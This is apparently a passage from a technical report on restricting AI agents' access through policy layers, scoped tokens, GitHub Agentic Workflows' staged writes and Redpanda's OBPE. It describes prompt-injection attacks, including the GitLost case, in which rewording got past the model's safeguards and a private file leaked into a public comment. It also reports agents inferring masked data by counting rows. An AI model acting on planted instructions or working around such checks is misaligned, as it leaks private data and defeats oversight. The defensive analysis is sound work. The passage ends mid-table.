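An update to the rules takes effect automatically if it permits nothing that the old rules forbid. Otherwise, it needs approval. Suppose the old rules permit comments of up to 500 characters in the mobile-app project only. An update that permits them only on issue 4112 in that project is narrower. An update that permits 100-character comments in every project is an expansion, despite the shorter limit, because it would allow a comment on issue 87 in the payroll project.

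Ji and colleagues' system, SEAgent, labels each tool by properties such as whether it returns unverified outside text and how sensitive its effects are. It also tracks how information moves between tools and agents. Its main rule blocks any moderately or highly sensitive change that follows from unverified outside text. When rules conflict, the more specific one applies, so a specific "allow" can override a general "deny". SEAgent allows the call if no rule matches.

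In FORGE, people write the rules before the task begins, or have a model translate them from a written policy. A rule can refer to everything that may have influenced a call. For example, it can block an outgoing email that depends on both an untrusted document and a secret file.

All three groups used AgentDojo, the set of simulated attacks mentioned earlier:

| System | Attacks that succeed without it | Attacks that succeed with it | Effect on ordinary tasks |
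| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Progent | 39.9% | 1.0% | Shi and colleagues report that utility held up |
| SEAgent | 39.1% | 0% | Ji and colleagues measured this on other tests |
| FORGE | 14.1% | 0.9% | Completion fell from 83.7% to 62.5% |

The rows aren't a ranking. FORGE's starting figure is lower partly because the agent already had a simple defence that repeated the user's request after each batch of tool results. Without that defence, FORGE reduced successful attacks from 25.2% to 1.7%. SEAgent's result of zero depends on correct labels, which a language model proposed and people corrected.

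Progent's protection came mostly from the rules it generated at the start. With rule updates switched off, attacks succeeded 2.5% of the time. On ASB, another set of attacks, Progent reduced the success rate from 70.3% to 3.9%. Most of the remaining failures involved harmful tools whose names and descriptions closely resembled those of tools the task needed.

SEAgent's main rule would be a poor fit for the tracker, because the agent reads text from customers and then writes comments. On API-Bank, a set of ordinary tasks, SEAgent raised only two false alarms, both when the agent recorded health data or booked an appointment after reading Wikipedia. Labelling Wikipedia as trusted, as Ji and colleagues suggest, would remove these false alarms, but anyone can edit Wikipedia, so it would also remove the protection against text planted there.

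FORGE's results show how much the choice of rules matters. Its rules for AgentDojo checked whether the user had asked for an action and where its target came from. Palumbo and colleagues also tried a stricter policy that blocked consequential calls once untrusted text had entered the context. Under the stricter policy, attacks succeeded 0.6% of the time, only slightly below the 0.9% under the first rules, and the agent completed just 33.2% of ordinary tasks.

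Rules can also help an agent do its job. In simulated airline customer service with Claude Opus 4.5, GPT-5.2 and Gemini 3.1 Pro, FORGE raised the average success rate from 74.7% to 81.5%, although Gemini's fell slightly. When FORGE blocked a call, it returned the reason, and the agent could try again. The rules encoded the same airline policies that the agents were supposed to follow, which makes the gain less surprising. The checks typically took less than a millisecond.

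### When approval becomes a reflex

A common objection to holding calls for a person's approval is that people stop reading the prompts. Silverlock gives no figures but compares the prompts to Windows User Account Control, which asked for confirmation so often that users clicked through it. Invariant Labs made a similar observation about users who choose "Always Allow". Christodorescu and colleagues list the human as a weak link in two of the 11 attacks on agents they studied. If the tracker agent proposes 45 comments and the employee has to approve each one, the employee could easily approve a comment that an attacker prompted.

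The obvious remedy is to ask for approval less often. If customers can read only five of the 45 issues, rule 3 reduces the prompts to five. On AgentDojo, only 6% of Progent's rule updates needed approval. The prompt also has to give the employee enough information to decide, such as the comment's full text and a note that customers can read it. An employee who sees only "add_comment on issue 4120" may approve it without judging it.

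Permanent exceptions also reduce the number of prompts, but they are riskier. SEAgent offers "Always allow this pattern" when it asks the user about a flow of information. If the employee chose this option for reading an issue and then commenting, the exception would probably also cover comments caused by a planted instruction, since these follow the same pattern.

The company can also limit the damage from a careless approval. Progent's main test simulated a user who accepted every expansion of the rules, and attacks succeeded only 1.0% of the time. When a person reviewed the initial rules and each expansion, no attacks succeeded. In the Agent Access Model, an approval covers one fixed resource for a limited time and can't exceed the task's ceiling. With the tracker's three rules, a careless approval releases one comment of at most 500 characters in one project. That comment could still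 embarrass the company in front of a customer, but it can't affect the other 39 projects.

The policy layer also needs a default for when nobody makes a choice. SEAgent blocks the call in that case. In Autonomous mode, Azure SRE Agent approves "ask" calls automatically, so if an administrator writes an "ask" rule for deletions, they go ahead without a question. To prevent them, the administrator has to write a "deny" rule.

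## Read-only agents with separate writing in GitHub Agentic Workflows

In GitHub Agentic Workflows, which GitHub has offered since February 2026, the agent can read a repository but can't change it. The agent describes the changes it wants, and after it has finished, a separate job with write permission makes or rejects them. This is called a staged write.

The system runs on GitHub Actions, which starts automated jobs in response to events in a repository, such as a new issue. Usually nobody watches these jobs, so the design can't rely on a person to refuse a bad tool call.

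### The threat model and four principles

According to GitHub's *Under the hood*, published in March 2026, the designers assumed that an agent would try to read and change things it shouldn't, communicate over unintended channels and misuse the channels it has. In an ordinary Actions job, every program can read the tokens stored on the virtual machine, so a misled agent with a command line could find them and post them in a comment. GitHub's *Security Architecture* also considers an attacker who runs arbitrary code inside the agent's container, the isolated environment where it works.

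GitHub's four principles are to defend in depth, keep secrets from the agent, stage and vet all writes, and log everything.

The defence has three layers. At the bottom, the virtual machine and its containers keep programs apart. Above that, the configuration determines which programs run, what they can connect to and which tokens they receive. At the top, the planning layer divides a run into stages and sets what passes from one stage to the next. Each layer limits the damage from failures above it but can't correct mistakes in the layers below. GitHub says that planning does not protect against an overly broad token, a limitation that mattered in July.

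GitHub keeps secrets from the agent by putting them in other containers. A proxy holds the key for the model and forwards the agent's requests to it. An MCP gateway starts the MCP servers and holds their credentials. A firewall lets the agent reach only listed sites. GitHub's *Safe Outputs MCP Gateway Specification* (2026), a working draft, is less strict about secrets. It allows the agent a token that can read but prohibits giving it any credential that can write.

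Coding agents also need compilers and other programs from the machine. GitHub gives the agents a read-only view of the machine's files and covers selected paths with empty directories. They can presumably still read any sensitive file the designers forgot to cover.

The firewall, the proxy and the gateway each log what passes through them. These logs help a company reconstruct an incident afterwards.

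### A workflow that may post one comment

Suppose the company keeps the mobile app's issues in a GitHub repository. Whenever someone opens an issue, an agent should look for earlier reports of the same problem. The workflow's author could write this file:

```
---
on:
  issues:
    types: [opened]
permissions:
  contents: read
  issues: read
network:
  allowed:
    - defaults
safe-outputs:
  add-comment:
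    max: 1
---
Search this repository for earlier reports of the same problem.
If you find any, post one comment that links to them.
```

The text below the second row of dashes is the prompt. The lines above it are settings:

- `on`, `issues` and `types: [opened]` start a run when someone opens an issue.
- `permissions` introduces the agent's rights. `contents: read` lets it read the code, and `issues: read` lets it read the issues.
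- `network`, `allowed` and `defaults` limit its connections to a standard list of basic infrastructure sites.
- `safe-outputs` introduces the changes the agent may request. `add-comment` allows comments, and `max: 1` allows one per run.

The example omits the model's credential. Its last setting is GitHub's default for comments, so the author could leave it out. Leaving out the whole `safe-outputs` section would not make the workflow read-only. GitHub's *Safe Outputs* explains that the agent could then request one new issue, unless the author sets `create-issue: false`.

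### One run from start to finish

Before the first run, the author compiles the file with `gh aw compile`. The compiler checks the settings and pins references to third-party code to exact versions where it can. In strict mode, the default, it rejects a file that gives the agent write permission. It then produces the lock file that GitHub Actions runs. The author can later edit the prompt without recompiling, but must recompile for changes to the settings to take effect.

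When somebody opens an issue, an activation job checks that the run is allowed to start and cleans the issue's text. It disables mentions of other users, converts HTML tags to harmless text and removes links to sites that aren't on the allowed list. This blocks several technical tricks but doesn't remove instructions written in plain English.

The agent then starts, reads issues through GitHub's MCP server and finds a match. To request a comment, it calls a tool:

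```
{"name": "add_comment",
 "arguments": {"body": "This looks like the crash in issue 4112."}}
```

The server that receives this call has no access to GitHub's API. It checks the request's format, adds the request to a file and returns an identifier such as `so_AbCdEf012345`, which confirms only that it has recorded the request. When the agent exits, GitHub stores the file for the next job. The draft specification forbids passing requests to that job through shared files, environment variables or a network connection, because GitHub's storage provides access control and a record of what was passed.

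Threat detection runs next unless the workflow's author has turned it off. A second agent without write permission reads the requested changes, any proposed code and the original prompt. It looks for leaked secrets, malicious code and actions outside the task, then returns a pass or a fail. On a fail, the workflow stops before making any changes. By default, this agent uses the same AI engine as the first, so text that misled the first may well mislead the second. Authors can add conventional scanners, such as TruffleHog, which searches for credentials.

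The last job cleans the comment, checks it against the limits and posts it. Only this job has the `issues: write` permission, so an attacker who has taken over the agent can't use it directly.

A company can also require a person's approval between detection and posting. GitHub recommends this for sensitive operations and enforces the pause outside the workflow, where the agent can't influence it. Without this approval step, a staged change can be posted without anyone reviewing it. A workflow's author can also allow the system to merge code automatically when certain conditions are met.

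An author can test a workflow in "staged mode", in which GitHub shows the changes it would have made without making them. The name is confusing because the system also stages writes in ordinary runs.

### What the checks can limit

The settings limit the kinds of change the agent can make. The sample agent can't close an issue because the author didn't list that operation, so the write job won't perform it. A few permitted operations have wider effects than you'd expect from their names. If the author allows `dispatch-workflow`, the agent can start up to three other workflows per run by default, and its own limits don't apply to those workflows.

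The maximum number applies to a single run. If a customer opens 50 issues and each one starts the workflow, the agent can post 50 comments. To stop this, the company would need a separate limit on how often the workflow runs.

By default, the write job posts the comment on the issue that started the run, whatever issue number the model supplies. This is a strong restriction, and the planned comments on 45 stale issues would require the author to relax it. The settings would become:

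```
safe-outputs:
  add-comment:
    max: 45
    target: "*"
```

The asterisk lets the agent choose which issues to comment on. An instruction planted in any one of them could now influence comments on 45 others that the attacker chooses, though only in this repository unless the author has allowed others.

The content checks remove strings that look like credentials, links to sites not on the allowed list, and various kinds of hidden markup. Removing these links also blocks some data leaks through URLs.

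None of these checks can verify that the comment is true or appropriate. A comment telling a customer that the next release fixes the crash passes even if nobody has fixed it. A comment containing a colleague's salary also passes, because "€8,500" doesn't look like a credential. The detection agent might notice the salary, but it sees only the stored files, so it can't open issue 4112 to check whether that issue describes the same crash. The draft specification acknowledges a remaining risk of "legitimate-seeming but contextually inappropriate content" within the limits. It suggests monitoring, anomaly detection and periodic review, which mostly help after the comment is public.

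### What the agent can read

By default, a workflow can't read the company's other private repositories. The workflow's author chooses which kinds of data the agent may read in the workflow's own repository, and can also shorten the agent's list of tools. If the workflow needs only issues, the author could drop `contents: read`, which would remove the agent's access to the code.

An integrity filter then sorts content by how much GitHub trusts its author and by whether the repository's maintainers have merged it. The levels, from most to least trusted, are `merged`, `approved`, `unapproved` and `none`. The MCP gateway removes anything below the chosen level before it reaches the agent. On public repositories, GitHub applies `approved` automatically, which restricts the agent to content from owners, members and collaborators.

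Like lockdown mode, this setting hides customers' bug reports, so the sample workflow would search for duplicates among only the few issues that staff had filed. The workflow's author could set `min-integrity: none`, as GitHub advises for sorting new issues or detecting spam. The agent could then find the duplicates, but anybody could plant instructions in what it reads. The filter is easiest to keep in workflows that don't need text from strangers.

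The filter may also miss the issue that starts the run. The filter works in the MCP gateway, but the activation job cleans that issue's text and can pass it to the agent without going through the gateway.

Stored notes need similar protection. An agent can save notes for later runs, so if it reads a stranger's issue that contains a planted instruction, it could save that instruction where a more trusted run will read it. The draft specification requires a separate storage branch for each integrity level, and only runs at that level can write to it.

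The limits on reading loosen most when an owner supplies a personal access token so that the agent can read other repositories. The `permissions` lines in the file restrict only the token that Actions issues for the run, not the owner's token. If the owner's token covers 40 private repositories, a misled agent can search all 40. Writing still goes through the separate job, but the limits on reading now depend on how the model behaves with a broad credential. GitHub's *Using at Scale in Organizations* recommends credentials from a GitHub App, an identity created for software, over personal tokens. The app's access also needs to be narrow, or the agent can read just as much.

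### The GitLost leak

In July 2026, researchers at the security company Noma published GitLost, an attack on such a workflow. Levi's *GitLost* describes a workflow that ran whenever someone assigned an issue. The agent read the issue's title and text and replied with a comment. It also had read access to the organisation's other repositories, including private ones.

The researchers opened an issue in a public repository, worded as a routine request from a sales executive. After an automation assigned the issue, the agent fetched a file from a private repository and posted its contents in a public comment. The model's safeguards had blocked some versions of the request, so the researchers varied the wording until one worked. Expert Insights' *Researchers Trick Misconfigured GitHub AI Agent Into Leaking a Private Repo* (2026) reports that Noma used its own repositories for the test.

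The limits on writing were unlikely to stop this comment, because the workflow's author had allowed comments and the agent posted one, on the issue that had started the run. If threat detection was on, it didn't block the comment. Checking who started the run might not have helped either, because an outsider wrote the issue but an automation assigned it.

In *GitLost Flaw Lets Attackers Trick GitHub AI Agent Into Leaking Private Repos*, Levi attributes the leak to the agent's permissions and inputs coming from different places. The agent could read private repositories, but it took in text from anyone who could open a public issue. The 2025 leak through GitHub's MCP server involved the same combination.

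Levi calls GitLost a critical vulnerability. A workflow with default access could not have read the private repository, so Levi's claim that an attacker needed only an organisation that used Agentic Workflows is too broad. Expert Insights is more accurate in blaming an over-permissioned workflow and a safeguard that the researchers could bypass with the right wording. But GitHub documents reading across repositories as a normal feature, and an owner who turned it on could reasonably have expected the checks on writing to catch a leak.

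Noma told GitHub about the weakness before publishing. According to The Next Web's *‘GitLost’*, Noma also proposed a warning in the documentation about sharing keys between repositories. GitHub had not yet added it and did not respond to questions from The Register, a technology news site. Callahan's *GitLost* (2026) reports that GitHub later described the vulnerable configuration in its documentation but issued no security advisory. This claim needs confirmation because Callahan's outlet calls its reporters "minds", which suggests automated writing.

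The most reliable remedy is again a token that covers only the public repository. SecurityWeek's *Critical Vulnerability Exposes GitHub Agentic Workflows to Prompt Injection* lists minimal permissions and limits on what agents can post publicly among Noma's recommendations. If a task needs private repositories, the workflow's author can send the agent's results to a private repository. A reviewer at an approval gate might also catch the leak if they recognised the text as private.

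### The cost of waiting

GitHub says that safe outputs add one extra job. Threat detection adds another, which includes another model call. The extra machine time and model use hardly matter for a workflow that runs once a week, but could become noticeable for one that runs on every comment in a busy repository.

Separating writing from the agent also delays changes. The sample comment appears only after the agent has exited and the remaining jobs have run, and an approval gate can add hours. A customer can wait a few minutes to learn that an issue is a duplicate, but a delay before the agent's first message during an outage would be more serious. As with any held request, the repository may also change during the wait.

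The agent stops before the write job runs, so it doesn't receive the result and can't correct a comment that the job rejects. GitHub partly compensates by letting the agent make requests that depend on earlier ones. Suppose the agent needs to create an issue that collects all reports of a crash, then comment on the customer's issue with a link. The new issue has no number yet, so the agent uses a temporary identifier, which the write job replaces with the real number. The agent can also mark the comment as dependent on the new issue, so that the comment fails if the write job can't create the issue.

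These dependencies don't undo completed changes. If the write job creates the issue and then fails to post the comment, the new issue stays. The agent also can't change its plan after a failure, since it had to state the plan before the first change took effect.

Delaying writes until the agent exits causes more problems for coding tasks than for comments. When a developer opens a pull request, the repository's tests often run automatically, and the developer fixes whatever fails. An agent with write access could do the same. In GitHub's system, the pull request doesn't exist until the agent has exited, so a later run has to deal with any failures. The agent can run some tests in its own container first, but not those that need secrets or outside systems it can't reach.

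A workflow author who finds these drawbacks too great can give the agent write permission directly or add custom jobs. GitHub warns that such changes bypass the limits in the `safe-outputs` list. The compiled lock file shows the permissions of every job, so a reviewer can use it to check whether a workflow separates reading from writing.

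## Full access behind a policy layer

GitHub can issue a token for a single repository, which keeps an agent out of a company's other private repositories. Some services offer no token that narrow. The main alternative is pass-through access, in which the agent's calls use a broad credential and only a policy layer restricts what the agent can read and write.

On the tracker, the policy layer would hold a credential for all 12,000 issues, and the agent would hold only a login for the policy layer. When the agent requests an issue, the layer checks its rules, fetches the issue with its own credential and returns as much of it as the rules allow. The tracker would return any issue the layer requested, so the layer would have to enforce every limit on the agent's access.

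### How it differs from token passthrough

Pass-through access has a similar name to token passthrough, in which an MCP server forwards the client's token to another service. In pass-through access, the policy layer does not forward the agent's login. It calls the tracker with a separate credential that the tracker issued to it. MCP permits this, and the Model Context Protocol's *Authorization Security Considerations* requires a server that calls another service to use a separate token issued by that service's authorization server.

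MCP bans token passthrough partly because two services may each rely on the other to check the token. Suppose a calendar connector accepts any token from the company's login system and forwards it to the tracker. The tracker's developers may assume that the connector has checked the token, while the connector's developers left that to the tracker. The MCP guidance also gives three other reasons. A thief with a stolen token could use such a server as a relay for extracting data. If several services accept the same token, someone who breaks into one of them can use it at the others. A server that only relays requests today may need its own controls later, and these are easier to add if it has used separate tokens from the start.

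The ban on forwarding tokens covers MCP servers, but some other systems allow forwarding. According to AWS's *Set up outbound authorization for your gateway*, Amazon's AgentCore Gateway, which evaluates Cedar rules, can pass a caller's token unchanged to web services hosted on AWS's own agent platform, though not to MCP servers. The gateway checks the token first, and the receiving service is responsible for validating it too.

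### Reasons to choose it

A policy layer can restrict a service that has no narrow credentials, such as the Prisma Postgres database mentioned earlier. *If Agents Were Angels, No Governance Would Be Necessary* (Millstone, Akidau and colleagues, 2026) points out that scoped tokens help only when the authorization server has the agent's assignment and every backend can enforce the resulting limits.

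The layer also keeps the rules in one place, so a company with ten services doesn't have to learn ten sets of scopes. In an example from Redpanda's *Manage Access Policies*, the documentation for a commercial policy layer, one Cedar rule lets a payments team call any tool on every server tagged `team=payments`.

A mistake in a central rule can affect everything the rule covers. In Redpanda's system, an agent's credentials and kill switch inherit the agent's tags. A rule that permits access by tag, without naming a type of resource or an action, therefore lets people create credentials for the agent and change its kill switch. A built-in rule that nobody can override stops agents from doing either, but it doesn't apply to people. Rule changes also take time to reach the programs that enforce them, so a newly saved ban may not take effect immediately.

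A third advantage is that the layer can use facts the backend doesn't have. *The Importance of Out-of-Band Metadata for Safe Autonomous Agents* (Akidau, Rockwood and colleagues, 2026) demonstrates this with agents that manage investment portfolios. The tool that retrieves a client's holdings has no argument for the client's identity. The gateway adds the identity based on the credential the agent logged in with, so a planted instruction can't make the model request another client's portfolio.

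The same demonstration sends trades above a set value to a person. Akidau and colleagues claim that an agent can't avoid this by misreporting a trade's value, because the comparison happens after the agent has finished. But in their description, the agent supplies the estimate of the trade's value. The claim holds only if the platform calculates the value itself.

Finally, a policy layer can remove part of a record. A token for the mobile-app project normally covers each issue in full, including a field with a customer's email address. A policy layer can return the issue's title and description without the address. Refusing the whole issue would also protect the address, but then the agent couldn't summarise it.

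### The gate, the altered request and the filtered answer

Millstone and colleagues call Redpanda's design Out-of-Band Policy Enforcement (OBPE). "Out of band" means that the rules and the agent's identity travel through channels that the agent can't read or change. A call that lists issues goes through these steps:

1. A connector, a program written for one backend, translates the call into an action, a resource and arguments. The platform supplies the agent's identity.
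2. The gate permits the call, denies it or holds it for an outside decision. A denied agent sees only a failure, without the name of the rule.
3. The layer alters the request. It can add conditions to the search and lower the number of records requested.
4. The backend runs the altered request on the broad credential.
5. The layer filters the answer. It drops forbidden records, then forbidden fields, and then masks sensitive text in the fields that remain. Last, it cleans up whatever surrounds the records, such as error messages.

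In step 5, the layer must drop issues before it removes fields. A rule might drop every issue whose `pay_related` field is true and also hide that field from the agent. If the layer removed the field first, it could no longer identify which issues to drop.

Steps 3 and 5 can enforce the same limit. Adding "project = mobile-app" to the search keeps other projects' issues from leaving the tracker. Checking the project again in the answer works with any backend, including one that ignores the added condition.

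Altering a proposed change is riskier than altering a search. Suppose an agent proposes to set an issue's status and assignee but is allowed to set only the status. The layer can delete the assignee from the request. Some services will then leave the existing assignee in place, but others will treat the missing field as empty and erase the name. OBPE therefore deletes a field only if the connector's description of the backend marks this as safe. Otherwise, the layer should deny the call. Millstone and colleagues add that the responsible user must be able to see when the layer has narrowed the agent's proposed change.

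### Combining the owner's rules with the agent's

OBPE has two sets of rules. The data owner, here the tracker's administrator, writes an owner policy that sets the most any agent can get. Whoever deploys the summary agent can write an agent policy, which can only reduce that. In plain notation, the combination is:

```
gate   = strictest matching result (deny, then hold, then permit),
         and deny if no owner rule permits the call
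query  = agent's query AND owner's condition AND agent policy's condition
limit  = smallest of the requested number and both policies' limits
fields = owner's fields ∩ agent policy's fields
```

Suppose the summary agent requests 500 issues that are open or high priority:

| | Request | Owner policy | Agent policy | Result |
| --- | --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Gate | | Permit | No objection | Permit |
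| Query | open OR high priority | not confidential | mobile-app project | (open OR high priority) AND not confidential AND mobile-app project |
| Limit | 500 | 200 | 100 | 100 |
| Fields | All | number, title, status, description | number, title, description, customer email | number, title, description |

The person who wrote the agent policy included customers' email addresses. The owner policy doesn't, so the agent won't receive them.

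The combined query needs its brackets because most query languages apply AND before OR. Without them, the tracker would read the query as "open, or else high priority and not confidential and in mobile-app", and return open issues from all 40 projects. If a connector can't guarantee the grouping, OBPE's design requires it to deny the call.

When restrictions are combined by taking a minimum, an intersection or an AND, their order doesn't affect the result, and adding another can never widen access. Millstone and colleagues prove both properties for the whole scheme, provided that every call goes through the layer, the platform identifies the agent correctly and the connector describes the backend accurately. Owner rules that permit something need separate treatment because adding one widens access. Rules that mask text also need it because they can interfere with each other, so the layer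 runs them in a fixed order.

The proof covers which records the agent may receive, but not which of them appear on the first page of results. For example, adding the project condition could raise the number of mobile-app issues in the first 100 results from three to 100, but it wouldn't reveal any that the owner's rules withhold.

If someone deploys the summary agent and forgets to write an agent policy, the agent gets everything the owner policy permits. With scoped tokens, an agent that was never issued one can't read anything. Because the owner policy may be the only policy restricting an agent, it needs particular care. Software can find contradictions in it but can't tell whether the administrator meant to permit what it permits.

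### The simulated Jira and ServiceNow trials

Millstone and colleagues tested OBPE on 71 tasks, using simulated versions of Jira (an issue tracker) and ServiceNow (a system for managing support requests). The agents ran on Claude Sonnet 4.6, Claude Haiku 4.5, GPT-5 and GPT-5 mini. The researchers compared 17 combinations of model and protection, running each task three times under each, for 3,621 trials.

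A trial counted as a security failure if protected data entered the model's context, an exact protected value appeared in the final answer, or a forbidden change went through. A trial was "safe and useful" if it had no such failure, the agent made the expected tool calls, and another model judged that it had done the permitted work without revealing a protected fact. These are the rates across all four models:

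| Outcome | No rules | Six rules in the prompt | Prompt rules and OBPE |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Any security failure | 63.3% | 57.6% | 0.2% |
| Protected data in context | 55.1% | 52.1% | 0.0% |
| Exact value in final answer | 27.5% | 3.7% | 0.2% |
| Forbidden change completed | 8.1% | 5.5% | 0.0% |
| Task fulfilled | 83.2% | 79.1% | 60.9% |
| Safe and useful | 19.1% | 22.0% | 58.9% |

The prompt rules cut exact disclosures in the models' final output from 27.5% to 3.7% but barely reduced how often protected data reached the models.

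The headline comparison, 57.6% against 0.2%, depends on counting protected data in the context as a failure. A prompt can't remove a field from a tool's output, so an agent failed as soon as it opened a permitted record containing a protected field. This definition is reasonable because data in the context can leak much later. But for a company concerned only with final answers, the relevant comparison is 3.7% against 0.2%, a much smaller gain.

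Fulfilment fell while safe and useful completion rose because, without OBPE, an agent that completed a forbidden update could still count as having fulfilled its task. OBPE was supposed to let five of the 71 tasks through unchanged, alter 54, hold two and deny ten. No agent could fulfil the 12 tasks it was supposed to hold or deny, so the highest possible score was 83%. Agents fulfilled 90.0% of the trials on unchanged tasks and 71.7% on altered ones.

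Many of the tasks were variants of one another, so Millstone and colleagues grouped them into 35 scenarios and gave each scenario equal weight. Twenty-three scenarios had a single task, and the largest had 12. The gains were smaller under this weighting. OBPE reduced security failures by 41.2 percentage points (95% confidence interval 27.7 to 54.9) and increased safe and useful completion by 21.8 points (9.5 to 35.2). When a second model judged the results, the rise in safe and useful completion was 19.1 points. No scenario had more security failures with OBPE than without it.

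In 20 of the tasks, Claude Opus 4.7 played an attacker that could rephrase its request after each reply, for up to 15 turns. It caused a security failure in 173 of 231 completed runs with prompt rules alone and in 2 of 227 with OBPE.

Readers have good reasons to discount these figures somewhat. Millstone and colleagues work for Redpanda, which sells the product, and they chose tasks to which the rules would apply. Only five tasks should have passed unchanged, which is too few to show how often OBPE would obstruct ordinary work. Newer models might follow prompt rules better than the ones tested. The researchers tested a simplified version of OBPE that could hold a call for approval but not carry it out afterwards. They also used models as judges without having people check the verdicts.

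The simulated systems also had a bug that affected 116 trials in the main comparison. The simulator mishandled the agent's query after OBPE had combined it with the policy's conditions, which widened the search in 65 cases. Leaving out all 116 changes the reduction in failures only slightly, to 40.5 points. But a real backend could have a similar bug, and a narrow token would limit the damage.

### Which controls made the difference

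Millstone and colleagues also added OBPE's controls one step at a time, using Claude Sonnet 4.6 with the prompt rules:

| Controls | No security failure | Task fulfilled | Safe and useful |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Gate, query limits and record filter | 46.7% | 75.1% | 21.8% |
| Also removing fields | 69.4% | 70.0% | 37.6% |
| Also masking fields and guarding writes | 88.6% | 65.7% | 51.9% |
| Also masking patterns in text | 100.0% | 66.2% | 63.0% |

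The first row is roughly what a well-scoped token could achieve, since its controls limit which operations the agent can use and which records it can reach. More than half of those trials still ended in a security failure, largely because permitted records contained fields the agent wasn't supposed to see. This is the study's best evidence for filtering answers. The exact share is a poor guide to other workplaces, because it depends on how many tasks involved a sensitive field. In the analysis that weights scenarios equally, removing fields lowered the failure rate by a further 9.9 percentage points, masking fields and guarding writes together lowered it by 7.8, and masking text lowered it by 11.5.

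The 100% in the last row was measured on these tasks and may not hold for others. Pattern masking caught the credentials that the researchers put into free text, but credentials usually have a recognisable form, unlike a salary written out in words.

A seemingly easier alternative is to leave the agent's tools unchanged and have a second model check what it writes. Millstone and colleagues tried this with Claude Haiku 4.5, which could pass or replace each message. Security failures occurred in 58.6% of trials with the reviewer and 0.0% with OBPE, while 19.7% and 63.0% of trials, respectively, were safe and useful. In the equally weighted analysis, OBPE's failure rate was 43.4 percentage points lower, with an interval from 27.7 to 59.3.

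The comparison of failure rates is somewhat unfair because the reviewer could not keep data out of the context. That limitation does less to explain why agents fulfilled 58.7% of tasks with the reviewer, against 66.2% with OBPE. The gap arose partly because the reviewer sometimes replaced a useful answer with a refusal. The reviewer also required 930 extra model calls, while OBPE required none.

### Reconstructed addresses and counted rows

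In four of the 1,065 trials with full OBPE, the final answer contained a protected email address that had never entered the model's context. The agents had inferred the address from a person's visible name and the usual form of the organisation's addresses. Some included it while explaining why they wouldn't reveal it. Two of these trials account for the 0.2% in the main comparison.

Removing a field doesn't hide its value if an agent can infer it from the remaining data. If the tracker shows that Yara Singh reported a crash, and every email address at her company has the form firstname.lastname, hiding the address field achieves little. The data owner would have to hide her name as well.

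In a separate trial, an agent probed a masked field by counting rows. It searched for records whose email address contained "@partner" and got two matches. It then tried "yara" and "singh" and got one match each. OBPE masked the addresses in the answers, but the backend ran the searches on the real ones. Neither the context nor the final answer contained an exact address, so the automatic checks recorded no failure.

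This is the problem of inferring hidden values from counts, described earlier. A ban on searching by hidden fields would stop the agent, but it would also disable any of the policy's own conditions that use those fields, such as "not confidential". A better rule would apply the ban only to conditions written by the agent. Millstone and colleagues mention this distinction and some other defences, such as query budgets, but didn't test any of them. A token for one project wouldn't have prevented the probing either, but it would have limited the agent to counting that project's records.

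### Tools that don't describe their answers

To remove the customer's email address from an issue, the policy layer has to know which field of the tool's answer contains it. An MCP tool can describe the fields it returns in an output schema, but MCP has supported these schemas only since mid-2025. Shi, Fu and colleagues (2026), in *Mitigating Taint-Style Vulnerabilities in MCP Servers via Security-Aware Tool Descriptions*, collected the definitions of 1,856 tools from 100 popular open-source servers and found that only 234 (12.6%) declared an output schema. They ranked servers by GitHub stars and left out those that generate tool definitions as they run, so commercial servers may differ.

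All 1,856 tools declared their inputs, so a policy layer can usually tell which arguments a call contains and use them to decide whether to allow it. Filtering what a tool returns is harder. If `get_issue` returns a single block of text, the layer can search for strings that look like email addresses, but it can't remove the customer's address as a separate field.

The server's developers can add a schema, or the company can write one and keep it in the policy layer. A schema in the policy layer works with servers the company doesn't control, but someone has to update it whenever the server's output changes. Suppose the tracker's developers add a field called `severance_amount`. OBPE returns only the fields on a list, so the new field stays hidden until someone adds it to the list. A layer that removed listed fields and returned the rest would pass the new field to the agent until someone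 listed it.

Even a list of permitted fields doesn't help when a field's meaning changes. If managers start writing pay details in issue descriptions, the layer will still treat the description as safe. Millstone and colleagues recommend giving each schema a named owner and updating schemas together with the rules. They didn't test any of this in their trials, because they wrote the connectors and simulated systems themselves and used simpler data than real systems hold.

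### The shared role in AgentCore Gateway

The credential behind a policy layer can become broad, as in AgentCore Gateway. Each gateway has one execution role, an AWS identity with its own permissions. According to AWS, all the tools configured to use this role share it, and its permissions are the upper limit on what any authorised caller can do through the gateway.

Suppose the company runs its tracker, payroll and refund tools as small programs on AWS's Lambda service and puts all three behind one gateway. The gateway's role needs permission to call all of them. The summary agent needs only the tracker, but if a rule permits too much, the role won't stop the gateway from calling payroll for the agent. If the company sets up the gateway through AWS's console, AWS can also create the role automatically and add the necessary permissions with each new tool, so the role can grow without anyone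 deciding that it should.

AWS recommends giving the role only the permissions its tools need, using separate gateways for tools with different levels of sensitivity, and using the policy engine to restrict callers. Separate gateways are the most reliable way to protect the payroll tool, because the agent can't reach payroll through a gateway whose role can't call it, even if the rules contain a mistake. The policy engine fails safely when the role lacks the permissions needed to evaluate rules, because the gateway then denies every tool call, even one that a rule permits.

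AgentCore's rules can stop a call, but Millstone and colleagues found no documented way for the rules to filter records out of an answer. They are assessing a competitor's product, and acknowledge that it can apply rules based on earlier events, which the released version of OBPE can't. According to AWS's *Types of interceptors*, customers can also attach interceptors to requests and responses. A company could presumably write one that removes fields, but it would have to maintain its own description of each tool's output.

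For MCP servers, a gateway can store a separate credential for each tool instead of using the shared role, or exchange the user's token for a narrower one that identifies both the user and the agent. Lambda programs support only the shared role. For AWS credentials in general, AWS's *AGENTSEC03-BP03 Implement least privilege with dynamic boundaries* recommends temporary credentials that last 15 to 60 minutes and grant only the permissions a task needs.

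The same guidance recommends passing the user's identity through the gateway so that the service behind it can apply that user's own limits. This would protect the payroll project from an agent working for someone who has no access to it. It wouldn't help with the summary task, because the employee who asked for the summary can read the payroll project too.

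## How the arrangements fail and what they cost

A call to a backend can go ahead only if both the token's scope and the policy layer's rules allow it.

```
possible calls = calls the token allows ∩ calls the rules allow
```

If one of them fails open, meaning that it lets everything through, the other is the only limit left. An arrangement without a policy layer behaves as if its rules allowed everything. For the tracker agent, the four arrangements would look like this:

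- **Broad credential alone:** the agent holds the employee's token, which can read and edit all 12,000 issues.
- **Scoped token alone:** the agent's token can read and comment on the 300 mobile-app issues.
- **Broad credential with a policy layer:** the agent logs in to the layer, which holds a credential for all 12,000 issues.
- **Scoped token with a policy layer:** the agent reads the 300 issues with its own token. The layer posts comments with a credential that can only comment in that project.

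| Failure | Broad credential alone | Scoped token alone | Broad credential with a policy layer | Scoped token with a policy layer |
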